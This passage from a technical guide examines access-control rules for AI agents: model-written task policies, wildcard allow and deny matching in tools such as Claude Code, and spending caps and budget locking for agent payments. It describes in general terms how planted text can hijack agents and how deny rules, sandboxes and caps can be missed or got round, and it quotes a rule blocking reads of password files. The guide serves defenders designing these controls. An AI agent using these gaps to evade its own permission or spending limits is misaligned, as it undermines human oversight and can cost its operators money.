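Other policies were too narrow. With Sonnet 5, Progent refused at least one needed call in 22 of the 92 tasks where the researchers could measure this. Its decisions also depended on the order of harmless steps, so it allowed an update to a standing order in one valid sequence but refused it in another. The agent still completed 87.6% of tasks, the same as without Progent, probably because it could often finish a task another way. When Haiku 4.5 wrote the policies, completion fell to 82.5%.

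Completion and leakage have to be measured separately. AC4A, another system in the test, also has a model write a policy for each task but never updates it. With Sonnet 5, AC4A's leakage was 0.111, close to Progent's, but the agent completed only 50.5% of tasks, down from 85.6% without AC4A. Policy updates seem to reduce leakage. When Sharma and colleagues froze Progent's first policy, leakage rose from 0.103 to 0.161, while the share of needed calls it allowed hardly changed.

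A model-written policy also varies from run to run. On identical input, Progent repeated between 92.5% and 95.3% of its decisions, so a user who submits the same request twice may get different permissions. Its total leakage stayed almost the same across runs.

The exact scores are somewhat uncertain because AgentDojo's own checks confirm only 27% of the labels, and the rest depend on Ajar's rules for what a task needs. The gaps between Progent and the two reference points are large enough to be reliable despite this, but its ranking against similar systems is not reliable.

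### PAuth and AgenTRIM

PAuth, which Sharma, Jiang and colleagues (2026) describe in *Beyond OAuth*, is meant to make the first policy exact. The API's server itself works out which calls the user's request implies. They argue that a general limit is no substitute, because a user who asks an agent to pay $100 hasn't authorized it to pay $499, even under a $500 cap.

Suppose the user asks the agent to pay a quarter of a Citi credit card balance from a Chase account. The user signs the request, and both banks receive it. At Chase, a model translates the request into a short program. Ordinary code then derives from the program the one transfer to expect, a payment to Citi of a quarter of the balance. When the agent asks Citi for the balance, Citi returns $1,200 with a digital signature. The agent passes this to Chase, which checks the signature and computes $300. If the agent tries to transfer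 $301 or pay anyone else, Chase asks the user.

The model that translates the request never reads emails, web pages or tool results, so planted text cannot influence it. But Progent's update step reads tool results and relies on the solver to catch the effects of any planted text.

The researchers tested PAuth on 100 tasks, mostly adapted from AgentDojo, after rewriting the vague ones to include every necessary detail. "Update my rent payment" became a request to set it to $1,200, for example, so somebody has to get the amount from the landlord's notice before PAuth can protect the payment. On the rewritten tasks, PAuth allowed all the needed calls without asking the user and blocked all 634 calls that deviated from the task. With the original wording, 71 of the 100 tasks ran without asking the user. The other 29 left out a value or referred to something like a file, so the user had to approve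 a call.

The developers argue that a faulty translation will nearly always cause an extra question, because a wrong rule is unlikely to match an attacker's account number by chance. This argument is convincing for wrong values but not for missing conditions. If the user says to pay only when the balance exceeds $1,000 and the translation omits that condition, Chase will accept a payment the user ruled out. The researchers found no such error in their 100 tasks. Adoption is the bigger obstacle, since each participating server has to run a model and read the user's request. For services that don't participate, an organization can run a trusted proxy that holds the tokens and performs the checks.

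*AgenTRIM* (Betser, Bose and colleagues, 2026) bases an agent's tool access on the calls the agent proposes. It divides tools into low-risk ones, which by default only read, and high-risk ones, which change something. If the agent proposes only low-risk calls, it may use any low-risk tool. If it proposes only high-risk calls, it may use only the tools it proposed. If it proposes both, the high-risk calls have to wait for a later step.

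This filter cannot stop a hijacked agent that proposes a single money transfer, because it then gives the agent the transfer tool. A second model provides the protection by judging each high-risk call against a summary of the task so far. The judge doesn't read the agent's reasoning, but the summary draws on tool results, so planted text may still reach the judge indirectly. Progent's model can be misled too, but it writes explicit rules that a person can inspect and a solver can compare.

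Betser and colleagues report low attack success and higher task completion than the unprotected agent on AgentDojo, at about 1.85 times the delay and twice the cost. They also report a clear loss of completed tasks with Progent, a result they took from Progent's paper as it stood in January 2026. There was no loss in the Ajar tests with Sonnet 5.

### Rules that the request doesn't contain

A policy derived from the user's request can contain only what the request implies. *Explicit Authorization Scope Improves LLM-Based Permission Checking in Coding Agents* (2026) tested Claude Code, Codex and Qwen Code, three coding agents that can approve some of their own actions. Of 143 actions outside the agents' authority, 132 (92%) broke rules that appeared in neither the user's request nor the tool outputs, so no model could have derived those rules from the task. When the researchers stated the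 rules explicitly and reran the tasks, none of the agents proposed a forbidden action.

This is a good argument for combining a model-written policy with a hand-written one. The person asking for a repair to the staging server may not mention that nobody may touch production, but the company can forbid access to production once for every task. Progent's generic policies can do this if they use explicit forbid rules.

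In *Compromise Is Not Consequence* (2026), the researchers supplied the permitted actions and resources for each task, and the model could not add to them. Fixed lists like this suit the shop's support agent better than a general assistant.

### What evaluations usually leave out

Most published tests report attack success and task completion, but neither measures false refusals. An agent may complete a task after three needless refusals, and the task will still count as completed. A useful evaluation also tests the rules on calls they should allow, in more than one valid order, and reports the share refused. If a model writes the rules, the test needs several runs.

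The evidence on delay is also incomplete. Progent needs one model call to write the first policy and up to two more after each tool call, so a task with five tool calls can require eleven extra model calls. Checking a call against a finished policy is quick by comparison. PAuth reports that translating the request costs $0.002 to $0.038 per task, but that figure doesn't show how long the bank's server will take. Ajar's results include neither delay nor cost.

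Figures on the work of maintaining rules are the hardest to find. *Security Risks in Tool-Enabled AI Agents* (2026) lists the effort of defining a complete policy as a drawback of this approach, along with errors that open a vulnerability or break a function. Unlike a benchmark's tools, a company's tools change with every release. Useful figures would include how many rules a team edits after each release and how long a legitimate call keeps failing before somebody corrects the schema.

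A team can measure false refusals on its own traffic by using a log-only mode, like those of OpenShell and AgentCore, and having someone who knows the work review the logged violations. The team also has to write its own tests for dangerous calls. For the email schema, these tests would include at least the two bad addresses in the table above, a `bcc` field and a recipient that isn't text.

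## Wildcard blocks and how they fail: Claude Code's permission rules

Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, checks the model's tool calls against a list of permission rules. A rule names a tool and usually adds a pattern in parentheses. For example, `Bash(npm test *)` covers any command that begins with `npm test`. Bash is the tool that runs commands on the user's computer, and the asterisk is a wildcard that stands for any text. Most rule lists contain wildcards because nobody can write out every command or address an agent might use. But wildcards make it harder to tell which calls a rule covers, so a deny rule can block calls its author meant to permit (over-blocking) or miss calls its author meant to block (under-blocking).

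### Deny, then ask, then allow

An allow rule lets a call go ahead without a prompt, an ask rule makes the user confirm it, and a deny rule blocks it. According to Anthropic's documentation, Claude Code checks the deny rules first, then the ask rules, then the allow rules, and applies the first match, so being more specific doesn't give a rule priority. This is a deny-overrides scheme with an ask level added between deny and allow.

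If no rule matches, the result depends on the permission mode. In Manual mode, Claude Code asks the user before it runs a shell command, unless it recognizes the command as read-only. In auto mode, a classifier reviews the call instead. The `dontAsk` mode refuses calls that would need approval instead of prompting the user, so it comes closest to default deny.

Anthropic illustrates over-blocking with `aws`, the command-line program for Amazon's cloud. The command `aws s3 ls` lists a customer's storage buckets and changes nothing. If a team allows that command and adds the deny rule `Bash(aws *)` to block the rest, the deny rule blocks the listing command too. Replacing the deny rule with an ask rule makes Claude Code prompt for every `aws` command, including the one the team allowed.

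| Rule added to allow `Bash(aws s3 ls)` | `aws s3 ls` | Other `aws` commands |
|---|---|---|
| Deny `Bash(aws *)` | Blocked | Blocked |
| Ask `Bash(aws *)` | Prompts | Prompts |
| None, in Manual mode | Runs | Prompt |
| None, in `dontAsk` mode | Runs | Refused |

The team wanted the result in the last row, which needs no deny rule at all.

Another allow rule cannot restore the listing command. Claude Code combines rules from the user's settings, the project's settings and, in many companies, managed settings that users cannot override. A deny rule in any of them blocks the call, so a developer who needs to list buckets has to persuade whoever wrote the deny rule to narrow it.

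Rules for files do allow limited exceptions. In a deny list, a pattern that begins with `!` cancels earlier patterns for the files it matches. For example, `Read(*.env)` followed by `Read(!sample.env)` blocks all files whose names end in `.env`, where programs often keep passwords, except those named `sample.env`. A `!` pattern has no effect at the top of the list, and it cannot cancel a rule from another settings file or reopen part of a directory that a rule blocks as a whole.

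Some restrictions can't be written as a pattern. *When "Do Not" Is Not deny* (Yan, 2026) examined 481 public CLAUDE.md files, in which developers write instructions for Claude Code. Built-in controls could enforce only 4.4% of the security rules in the sample under the strictest standard for matching a control to a rule, and about 16% under the loosest. One rule was to publish a package only when cutting a release. A deny rule on the publishing command would block it on release day too, because the command is the same whether or not a release is under way. The shop would have the same problem if its support agent were supposed to cancel orders only at the customer's request.

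The language model that sorted the rules for Yan often missed such conditions and tended to count a rule as enforceable if it mentioned a command that a pattern could block. Yan estimates that only 35% of the matches it reported were correct. A person writing a deny rule can easily make the same mistake. Yan's sample consists mostly of recent, little-known projects, and some teams may enforce their rules by other means.

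### What `deny *` does under three rule orders

People who have configured firewalls often end a list with a line that refuses everything else. Suppose the shop wants an agent to have read-only access to its API and writes:

```
allow GET /v1/*
deny *
```

The agent sends a GET to `/v1/orders/1042` and a POST to `/v1/refunds`. Under first match, the first line allows the GET, and the POST falls through to the second line, `deny *`, which blocks it. Here `deny *` is harmless because it only makes default deny explicit. Under deny-overrides, `deny *` matches both requests and overrides the allow rule, so the agent can't make any calls.

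OpenCode's *Permissions* describes yet another order. In this open-source coding agent, the last matching rule wins, so the broad rule goes first and the exceptions follow.

| Rule order | Allow line first | Deny line first |
|---|---|---|
| First match | GET passes, POST refused | Both refused |
| Last match | Both refused | GET passes, POST refused |
| Deny-overrides | Both refused | Both refused |

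Under deny-overrides, whoever writes the rules has to delete the deny line and make refusal the default. Varlock's *Proxy routing rules* recommends this for its HTTP proxy, where block rules always win. To permit only part of a host, it advises operators to turn on the `strict` setting, which refuses any request without a matching allow rule, and then allow that part. Without `strict`, the proxy forwards unmatched requests untouched.

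Janee, a program that stores API keys and makes requests on an agent's behalf, has contradictory documentation about the order in which it checks rules. *Policies & Scoping*, on Janee's website, says that the program reads rules from top to bottom and stops at the first match, and that every list should end with `deny: "*"`. But the README in Janee's code repository says that the program checks deny patterns first and that they always override allow patterns. If the README is right, an operator who follows the website's advice blocks every request. The two may describe different versions, since the website puts all the rules in one sequence and the README has separate lists for allow and deny. An operator can find out which order an installed copy uses by sending one request that should pass.

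According to Janee's README, if a set of permissions contains at least one rule, Janee refuses requests that no rule matches. If it contains no rules, Janee allows everything. Somebody who deletes an agent's only allow rule to withdraw its access would therefore give it full access to that service. By contrast, an AgentCore engine with no policies refuses every call.

Products also differ in how they rank ask rules. SRE Agent, which manages systems on Microsoft's Azure cloud, checks deny rules, then allow rules, then ask rules, according to Microsoft's *Tool Access Policies*. When a call matches both an allow rule and an ask rule, SRE Agent proceeds, but Claude Code prompts. Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, would also prompt, because it applies the most restrictive matching rule, according to OpenAI's *Rules*. A team that copies its rules from Claude Code or Codex to SRE Agent could therefore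 lose its approval step.

### What an asterisk covers

The asterisk also has different meanings, sometimes within the same product.

| Kind of pattern | What `*` matches |
|---|---|
| Command in Claude Code | Any text, including spaces |
| File path in Claude Code | Text within one segment (`**` crosses segments) |
| Domain in Claude Code that begins with `*.` | Subdomains at any depth, but not the domain itself |
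| Domain in Claude Code with `*` in another position | Text between two dots |
| Path or command in OpenCode | Any text, including slashes |
| Permission in an Azure role | Text that can span several segments |

In an allow rule, an asterisk that matches across slashes is riskier, because `GET /orders/*` then also covers `/orders/1042/notes` and may give the agent access to the staff notes. In a deny rule, an asterisk that stops at a slash is riskier because it blocks fewer paths, as in NVIDIA's example rules for GitHub.

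The character before the asterisk also matters. In Claude Code, `Bash(ls *)` requires a space after `ls`, while `Bash(ls*)` also matches `lsof`, a different program. Similarly, the path pattern `/orders*` can match `/orders-archive`, which `/orders/*` does not. As an exception to the space requirement, `Bash(ls *)` also matches `ls` on its own if the final asterisk is the rule's only wildcard. In other matchers, `/orders/*` may not match `/orders`, so an author should test the shorter path separately.

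### Blocks that match too little

A pattern matches the text of a call, but people usually write deny rules to prevent an effect. Chen and Lin (2026), in *One Goal, Many Commands*, tested 1,709 blocklists from public projects and found that, depending on the file operation, 69.0–98.6% of the lists that targeted the operation left another way to perform it. APIs have the same problem. Suppose the shop denies GET on `/customers/export` to keep its agent from downloading the customer list. If `/reports/customers` returns the same records, the agent can still download them there. A second deny rule would close only that route, so it is better to allow just the endpoints the agent needs. If the agent needs too many to list, the shop can give it a token that cannot read customers in bulk.

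Rules can also fail when a parameter is missing. Claude Code's deny and ask rules can test a field in a tool's input. For instance, `Agent(model:*)` matches any call that starts a subagent with an explicitly chosen model, but not one that omits the model. Suppose the shop's pricing API has an optional `environment` parameter that can be `test` or `live`, and the server assumes `live` when the parameter is missing. A request without the parameter could then change real prices even if a rule denied `environment=live` or `environment=*`, because the rule checks the request before the server fills in the default. The shop should allow only requests with `environment=test`, so that a request without the parameter fails. A schema that requires the field and permits only `test` would also work.

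Each of these rules can test only one field, which must be at the top level of the input. If the shop's gateway worked this way, the shop could not deny only the refunds that are both in a foreign currency and to a bank account. It would have to deny every refund of one kind or the other, including some legitimate ones. It also could not test a currency stored inside a nested `payment` record.

Many systems accept several names for the same thing. Claude Code compares a field's value with the rule before it converts the value to a standard form, so `Agent(model:opus)` matches the short name `opus` but not the full ID of the same model. An API might accept both `region=eu` and `region=europe`, and a rule that denies the first would not block the second. Converting names to one form before checking them fixes this. Claude Code does so in some other places. For example, a deny rule for a skill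 (a packaged set of instructions) matches the skill under any of its names. If the shop cannot change its enforcement point, it can allow one spelling of each permitted region and refuse all others.

Some deny rules never take effect. When Claude Code loads a settings file, it skips any MCP tool rule that contains parentheses, so a team that tries to deny a refund tool only for certain values gets no block at all. Claude Code lists the skipped rule in a dialog at the start of an interactive session and in the output of `claude doctor`, but nobody is there to read the dialog when an agent runs overnight on a server. Claude Code also accepts `Write(docs/**)` but never matches it, because it checks file changes only against `Edit` rules.

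An API gateway might have the same problem with a deny rule that contains a full web address where the gateway accepts only a method and a path. If the gateway drops that rule and loads the rest, the result is the same as when Cedar skips a forbid policy. The gateway should not start if it cannot load a deny rule, but a warning is enough for a faulty allow rule.

A well-formed rule can also contain the wrong name. Claude Code displays one of its tools as "Stop Task", but rules must use the name `TaskStop`. Claude Code warns at startup when a deny or ask rule names an unknown tool, except when the name contains an underscore or an asterisk. All MCP tool names contain underscores, so a misspelled deny rule for `mcp__shop__delete_customer` produces no warning. The exemption probably exists because Claude Code may not yet have the list of tools a server offers. An HTTP rule could contain the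 same mistake, such as `/refund/*` for an API whose path is `/refunds/*`. The enforcement point should compare each rule with the API's operations, as AgentCore does with its schema, and report an error when a deny rule matches none of them.

### Why allow wildcards have stricter limits

Claude Code accepts `mcp__*` as a deny rule, which blocks every MCP tool. It ignores the same pattern in an allow rule, where a wildcard may appear only after a server's full name, as in `mcp__github__get_*`. If `mcp__*` worked as an allow rule, every server the user connected later could run all its tools without a prompt. Unlike deny rules, allow rules also cannot test a single input field. Anthropic explains that one acceptable value doesn't make the whole call safe.

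Even when both kinds of rule accept a pattern, the deny rule may cover more:

- As a deny rule, `secrets/**` covers a directory named `secrets` at any depth below the current one. As an allow rule, it covers only the one directly inside the current directory.
- A symbolic link is a file that points to another file. A deny rule applies if either the link or its target matches, but an allow rule applies only if both do.
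- As a deny rule, `mcp__reports` also covers a server named `reports__v2`. As an allow rule, it does not.

In each case Claude Code refuses when in doubt, as Saltzer and Schroeder's fail-safe defaults would require. This sometimes blocks too much, so somebody who wants to block only the `reports` server has to deny its tools one by one or rename a server.

The same asymmetry makes sense for HTTP rules. A gateway could accept `deny DELETE *` but require every allow rule to specify a method and the first part of a path. The shop could then block all deletions in one line, but nobody could open the whole API by writing `allow *`.

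Wildcards of both kinds also cover more as an API grows. If the shop's developers add GET `/v1/payouts`, which lists transfers to the shop's bank account, `allow GET /v1/*` lets the agent read it from the first day. In a deny rule, this growth is usually an advantage. `deny * /v1/admin/*`, for example, blocks new administrative operations as soon as they appear. But it may also block a harmless status check that the developers put under `/v1/admin`, and under deny-overrides someone must then rewrite the deny rule to make the check available.

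Microsoft's *Create or update Azure custom roles using the Azure portal* recommends listing permissions explicitly, because a wildcard also grants matching permissions that Microsoft adds later. Yet Azure's built-in Contributor role uses a wildcard for its permitted actions, and Microsoft's *role definitions* explains that this wildcard includes actions that don't exist yet.

*Quantifying Azure RBAC Wildcard Overreach* (Parisel, 2025) measured how far badly placed wildcards can reach. For each of the 15,481 actions Azure had at the time, a program replaced part of the name with a wildcard and searched for the version that matched the most distantly related actions. For about 39% of actions, it found a wildcard that also matched actions in another service. For example, `Microsoft.Hardwar*ers/delete` covers deleting both hardware orders and clusters of hardware security modules, the devices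 that protect encryption keys. Because the program searched for the worst patterns, the 39% figure doesn't measure how often the wildcards people write are this broad. Microsoft's built-in roles don't put wildcards in the middle of a name, but Azure lets customers do so in custom roles.

### What a deny rule needs beneath it

Anthropic states that a deny or ask rule for a Bash command "isn't a security boundary around the program". The rule covers the form of the command that the model usually produces, so it helps prevent ordinary mistakes, such as an agent trying to push unfinished code because pushing is the normal next step. It protects much less against an agent that has read planted instructions or is looking for another way to finish its task.

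For limits that don't depend on a command's text, Anthropic recommends a sandbox in which the operating system restricts the files and hosts that shell commands can reach. The restrictions also apply to any programs they start. But Yan points out that the sandbox's list of allowed domains blocks other hosts only if the operator also turns on a strict setting or a managed equivalent. Otherwise, Claude Code asks the user about them.

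A wildcard in a permission rule can loosen the sandbox. The rules `WebFetch` and `WebFetch(domain:*)` both cover every address for Claude Code's page-fetching tool, but only the second adds its pattern to the sandbox's domain list. If an operator allows `WebFetch(domain:*)` so that the agent can read web pages, shell commands in the sandbox can also reach any host.

Anthropic also recommends hooks, programs that the operator writes and Claude Code runs before each tool call. A hook can examine the whole call and check conditions that no pattern can express, such as whether a release is under way. In Claude Code, a hook can block a call that an allow rule permits, but it cannot approve one that a deny rule blocks. In Microsoft's SRE Agent, a hook's approval overrides even a global deny rule, although only administrators can create hooks and the system logs each override.

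In Claude Code, a mod, which is a type of extension that users install, can approve a call that a deny rule blocks if the machine has no managed settings and the user isn't logged in through a Team or Enterprise plan. If the machine has managed settings or the user is logged in through one of those plans, the deny rule holds by default. A company that relies on deny rules should therefore deploy managed settings, even if it has only a few rules to put in them.

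Claude Code's sandbox covers shell commands but not MCP tools. If the shop's agent issues refunds through an MCP server, the sandbox will not stop a refund that a deny rule misses. A tool gateway or the API's server has to block it, for example through a token that cannot issue refunds.

### Testing a wildcard rule

The best way to see what a wildcard covers is to list the operations it matches. Parisel's program does this for Azure roles. It expands the permitted patterns and the exclusions into two lists of actions, then subtracts the second from the first. In one example, a role permits `Microsoft.AAD/*` but excludes actions that end in `read` or `delete`, and the program returns the five actions that remain.

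The shop can use the same method for its API. Suppose it allows `GET /v1/*` and `POST /v1/refunds`, denies `* /v1/exports/*`, and refuses everything else by default. In its gateway, deny rules override allow rules, and `*` can match across slashes. The API's first release has six operations, and the second adds three. The `{id}` in a path stands for an order or customer number.

| Operation | Release | Matching rules | Result |
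|---|---|---|---|
| GET `/v1/orders` | 1 | Allow | Allowed |
| GET `/v1/orders/{id}` | 1 | Allow | Allowed |
| GET `/v1/customers/{id}` | 1 | Allow | Allowed |
| DELETE `/v1/customers/{id}` | 1 | None | Refused |
| POST `/v1/refunds` | 1 | Allow | Allowed |
| GET `/v1/exports/orders` | 1 | Allow and deny | Refused |
| GET `/v1/exports/customers` | 2 | Allow and deny | Refused |
| POST `/v1/refunds/bulk` | 2 | None | Refused |
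| GET `/v1/payouts` | 2 | Allow | Allowed |

The agent can use four operations with the first release and five with the second, although nobody has changed a rule. The only new permission is GET `/v1/payouts`, so the reviewer doesn't have to reread the whole table. A support agent doesn't need the shop's bank transfers, so the shop should replace `GET /v1/*` with rules for orders and customers.

The expansion also reveals several of the mistakes described above. If the deny rule were `/v1/export/*`, it would match no operations, and GET `/v1/exports/orders` would appear as allowed. If the rules ended with `deny *`, the list of allowed operations would be empty. To catch such errors, the test has to use the enforcement point's own matching code and rule order. A separate script might handle `*` or a missing slash differently, so a faulty rule could pass the test and then fail in use.

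The list of operations can come from the API's published description or from a catalog like the one Azure provides. The list will omit undocumented operations. Deny rules may miss them too, which is another reason to refuse everything that no allow rule matches. For a GraphQL API, the list has to contain root fields instead of paths.

Expansion doesn't cover the values in a call, so the shop also needs some complete test requests. For the pricing API, these would include one request without `environment`, and for the regional API, one with each accepted name for the same region. Codex lets authors store such examples with each rule, in one list of commands the rule should match and another of commands it should not, and checks both lists when it loads the rules. OpenAI also provides a command that shows the decision for a proposed call and the rules that produced it. The most useful examples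 are those whose result would change if the pattern changed slightly.

An API's owner may release new operations without telling customers, so the test should also run on a schedule. For allow rules, the gateway can enforce the approved expansion instead of the wildcard, which blocks new operations until somebody has reviewed them. Deny rules should keep their wildcards so they cover new operations immediately.

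## Spending caps: agent wallets and the Agent Payments Protocol

An agent with access to a paid API can run up a large bill without breaking any allow rule, either by repeating a permitted call thousands of times or by accepting a very high price once. A per-call cap limits the cost of one call, and a period cap limits the total cost of all calls in a stated period. Counting the spending correctly is harder than choosing the amounts, especially when several calls run at once or several companies take part in a payment.

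### How an agent pays under x402

x402 is a protocol for paying for individual HTTP requests. Its name comes from the HTTP status code 402, "Payment Required", which had long gone unused. The x402 project launched the protocol in May 2025 and counted more than 100 million payments in the first few months. Google, Visa and Stripe back other payment protocols for agents, but x402 has by far the most traffic, according to *Free-Riding the Agentic Web* (2026).

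Suppose the shop has a purchasing agent that searches a supplier's catalog, and the supplier charges for each search. A payment takes five steps:

1. The agent sends a GET request to the supplier's `/search` endpoint.
2. The server replies with status 402 and one or more ways to pay, each with an amount, a currency and a recipient's address.
3. The agent picks one and has its wallet sign an authorization for the payment.
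4. The agent repeats the request with the signed authorization in a header.
5. The server collects the payment and returns the search results with a receipt.

For the last step, most servers use a facilitator, a service that checks the signature and submits the payment to a blockchain (a shared public ledger). Cloudflare says the facilitator doesn't hold any funds.

The sample reply in x402's *Payment Schemes* gives the price of weather data as "1000" in USDC, a digital currency worth one dollar per unit. Software counts USDC in millionths, so the price is a tenth of a cent. Anyone who writes a cap for such payments has to state it in millionths too.

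AgentCore's condition on refunds below $500 reads the amount from the agent's call. With x402, the agent's first request contains no amount, because the server sets the price in its reply. An enforcement point that checks only the first request therefore can't limit the cost, and the check has to happen after the server quotes the price and before the payment is signed.

x402 has three payment schemes. With `exact`, the agent authorizes the quoted price. Fireblocks' *x402 concepts* explains that this authorization covers a single transfer, so there is no standing permission to charge the wallet again. With `upto`, the agent authorizes a maximum and the seller charges for actual usage. `batch-settlement` collects many small payments and settles them together. Fireblocks recommends `exact` unless the cost really varies, since `upto` leaves the final amount to the seller's side.

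### Limits at the point of signing

Fireblocks, which stores digital assets for companies, offers an x402 client that lets an agent pay from a vault, its term for a wallet account. The agent never holds the vault's keys. It must ask Fireblocks to sign each payment, and Fireblocks first checks the request against the company's policy rules. Fireblocks says the client "enforces no spending limit of its own". This arrangement is sound because the limits in the policy rules still hold if an attacker takes over the agent's computer.

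Fireblocks recommends four rules for the vault:

- a cap on each transaction, set close to the price of one small payment (1 USDC or less, for example)
- an hourly or daily cap, which it calls a velocity cap
- an allowlist of currencies and recipient addresses
- a threshold above which a person has to approve the payment in a mobile app

The approval threshold has to be lower than the transaction cap, or Fireblocks will reject the payment before anyone can approve it. With a threshold of $25 and a cap of $60, small payments go through automatically, a $40 payment waits for approval, and a $70 payment fails. An agent could avoid approval by splitting the $40 payment into two of $20, if the seller accepts that. Only the hourly or daily cap limits how much it can spend this way. Fireblocks also recommends requiring two approvers for any change to the rules.

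The client has its own settings, which are weaker because they run beside the agent. One makes the payment tool return a preview and sign only after a second call with `confirmed=true`. The model makes both calls, so this is a human approval only if the surrounding program shows the preview to a person. Another setting restricts payments to listed web hosts. This helps when many sellers receive money through the same settlement contract (a program on the blockchain), because an allowlist of addresses can't tell those sellers apart.

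Circle, the company that issues USDC, enforces limits on its agent wallets as well. An operator who sets custom transfer limits must set four: per transaction, per day, per week and per month. None may exceed the next. If the operator sets no custom limits, Circle applies a default of 100 USDC per month. An operator can add separate limits for one blockchain, and the stricter value then applies. The required order prevents an operator from setting a daily cap that could never take effect because the monthly cap is lower. But the four caps can be equal, so if each is 100 USDC, a single payment can use up the month's allowance.

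Circle asks the operator to confirm each change with a one-time code sent to the email address of the agent's session. The agent must not be able to read that mailbox, or it could raise its own limits. Changing an allowlist of recipients takes two commands, one to reset the old rules and one to set the new ones. The operator should pause the agent between the two, since the old list apparently no longer applies after the first.

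The transfer limits count only USDC and EURC, Circle's euro currency. For everything else, Circle recommends an allowlist of the contracts the agent may call, which the operator has to set up separately on each blockchain.

### Why a balance is not a budget

Fireblocks describes a vault's balance as a hard ceiling on what the agent can spend and advises companies to keep it small. This is good advice, because the balance limits the loss even if the policy rules are badly written. But the balance doesn't limit how fast the agent spends or what it buys. If the shop deposits $500 for the month, the agent can spend it all in the first minute. Without a policy rule, a funded vault pays whatever the seller asks. Fireblocks' client can check before each payment that the vault holds enough money, but Fireblocks warns that this check is not a spending limit.

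The ceiling also disappears if the account refills itself. In the forum thread *Should all users have hard spending caps?*, an OpenAI customer reports that a former developer abused one of the company's API keys. The account's credits, normally topped up about once a month, were topped up twice in less than 24 hours. The company usually spent about $200 a month, but OpenAI allowed it up to $200,000. Fireblocks' advice to refill a vault on a schedule avoids this if the amount is fixed, but a refill triggered by a low balance needs its own cap.

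### What each cap permits

Let B be the balance at the start of a day and D the daily cap. If nobody adds money, the most the shop can lose that day is the smaller amount, min(B, D). With a cap of $50, that limit is $50 if the wallet holds $500 and $30 if it holds $30. If top-ups during the day total T, the limit becomes min(B + T, D), so with unlimited top-ups the limit is D.

This assumes the loss stays within one calendar day. If the cap resets at midnight, the agent can spend $50 at 23:59 and another $50 at 00:01, a total of 2D in two minutes, without exceeding the cap. A rolling window prevents this by adding up the past 24 hours of payments whenever the agent tries to pay. It would refuse the second $50 until 24 hours after the first.

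A rolling window requires a record of the time of each payment, while a calendar cap needs only one running total. An operator who can't get a rolling window can add a shorter cap. An hourly cap of $10 that resets on the hour reduces the most the agent can spend around midnight from $100 to $20. Circle's guide doesn't specify whether its caps follow the calendar, so an operator should allow for twice the daily cap.

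The time zone in which a daily cap resets also matters. Anthropic's *Claude apps gateway spend limits* describes a gateway that companies can run to share access to Claude models, with daily caps that reset at midnight UTC. That is 4 or 5 p.m. in California, when many agents are working, so a busy team could spend two days' allowance in one afternoon even without an attack.

The shop needs both a per-call cap and a period cap. A per-call cap alone doesn't limit the total. If each call may cost up to $1 and the agent makes one call per second, it can spend $3,600 in an hour. With only a period cap, one wrong purchase can use the whole amount.

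### A search endpoint and a purchase endpoint

One pair of caps rarely suits every endpoint. Suppose the supplier charges $0.02 for a search, while an order of spare parts can cost $60. A per-call cap that permits the order would also permit a search for $60. The shop therefore sets separate caps for each endpoint and an overall daily cap:

| Endpoint | Per-call cap | Daily cap |
|---|---|---|
| GET `/search` | $0.05 | $20 |
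| POST `/orders` | $60 | $100 |
| Both together | None | $110 |

A call has to satisfy all the caps that apply to it. If it costs c, its endpoint has a per-call cap p and a daily cap D₁, and the overall daily cap is D₂, the call may proceed only if

- c ≤ p
- S₁ + c ≤ D₁, where S₁ is what the agent has already spent on this endpoint today
- S₂ + c ≤ D₂, where S₂ is what it has spent on both endpoints today

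By noon, the agent has made 200 searches for $4.00 and has ordered nothing. It then makes these calls in order:

| Call | Result | Search total | Order total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Search for $0.02 | Allowed | $4.02 | $0 |
| Search for $0.50 | Refused, above the per-call cap for searches | $4.02 | $0 |
| Order for $60 | Allowed | $4.02 | $60 |
| Order for $45 | Refused, orders would reach $105 | $4.02 | $60 |
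| Order for $40 | Allowed | $4.02 | $100 |
| 299 searches for $0.02 each | Allowed | $10.00 | $100 |
| Search for $0.02 | Refused, the overall total would exceed $110 | $10.00 | $100 |

The last search fails even though the agent has used only half of its search allowance. The endpoint caps add up to $120, so the overall cap of $110 takes effect only on days when the agent uses both endpoints heavily. An overall cap of $120 or more would never take effect, and one of $100 or less would make the daily cap on orders redundant.

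The search cap also leaves at least $90 for orders. Without it, an agent stuck in a loop could spend the whole $110 on searches.

A wallet may not be able to apply these caps, because a signed payment contains the recipient and the amount but not the endpoint. If the supplier uses one address for searches and orders, the wallet can distinguish them only by price. *Free-Riding the Agentic Web* also lists cross-resource substitution among the flaws in x402 deployments, so a payment is poor evidence of which resource it was for. The shop should enforce the endpoint caps in its tool gateway and set the $110 cap in the wallet, where it also covers calls that bypass the gateway.

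### Parallel calls that spend the same money

*APEX* (2026), a proposed system for controlling agents' payments to APIs, blocks a request if `spent_today + amount > daily_budget`. `spent_today` counts only payments that have already gone through, so the rule can fail when an agent makes several calls at once, as can AgentCore's policies on completed calls.

Suppose an agent has spent $90 of its $100 daily budget and sends two $8 requests at the same time. The system checks each request against the $90 already spent and allows it because the total would be $98, but the two requests together bring the total to $106. Ten such requests would bring it to $170.

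The remedy is to reserve the money before sending the request:

1. Lock the counter so that no other call can read or change it.
2. Add up what the agent has spent, what other calls have reserved and the most this call can cost. If the sum exceeds the cap, release the lock and refuse the call.
3. Otherwise, record the reservation, release the lock and send the request.
4. When the final price is known, add it to the spending and cancel the reservation.

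In the example, the first request reserves $8. The second check then adds $90, $8 and $8, gets $106 and refuses.

If a request times out, its money should stay reserved until someone finds out whether the payment went through. If the shop's counter released the money after every timeout, a retry could pay for the same order twice while the counter recorded only one payment. Similarly, once a payment has a transaction ID, Fireblocks' facilitator doesn't mark it as failed after a temporary error, since the transfer may still arrive.

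In *Token Budgets*, Khan (2026) tested several agents that shared one budget. The group overspent in all 30 runs when each agent read the remaining amount without coordination, but in none of 30 runs when the agents used a properly locked counter. Khan also collected 63 confirmed cases of budget overruns from public reports about 21 software projects for building agents. The cases don't measure how common overruns are, because Khan looked only for projects that had them, but independent teams evidently keep making the same mistakes.

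Khan's own remedy is a budget type for the programming language Rust. If a developer tries to copy a budget or use it again after giving it to another agent, the program doesn't compile. For a single agent, a four-line counter in Python prevented overspending just as well. The Rust type is useful mainly when agents delegate work, because it doesn't depend on every developer remembering to use the lock.

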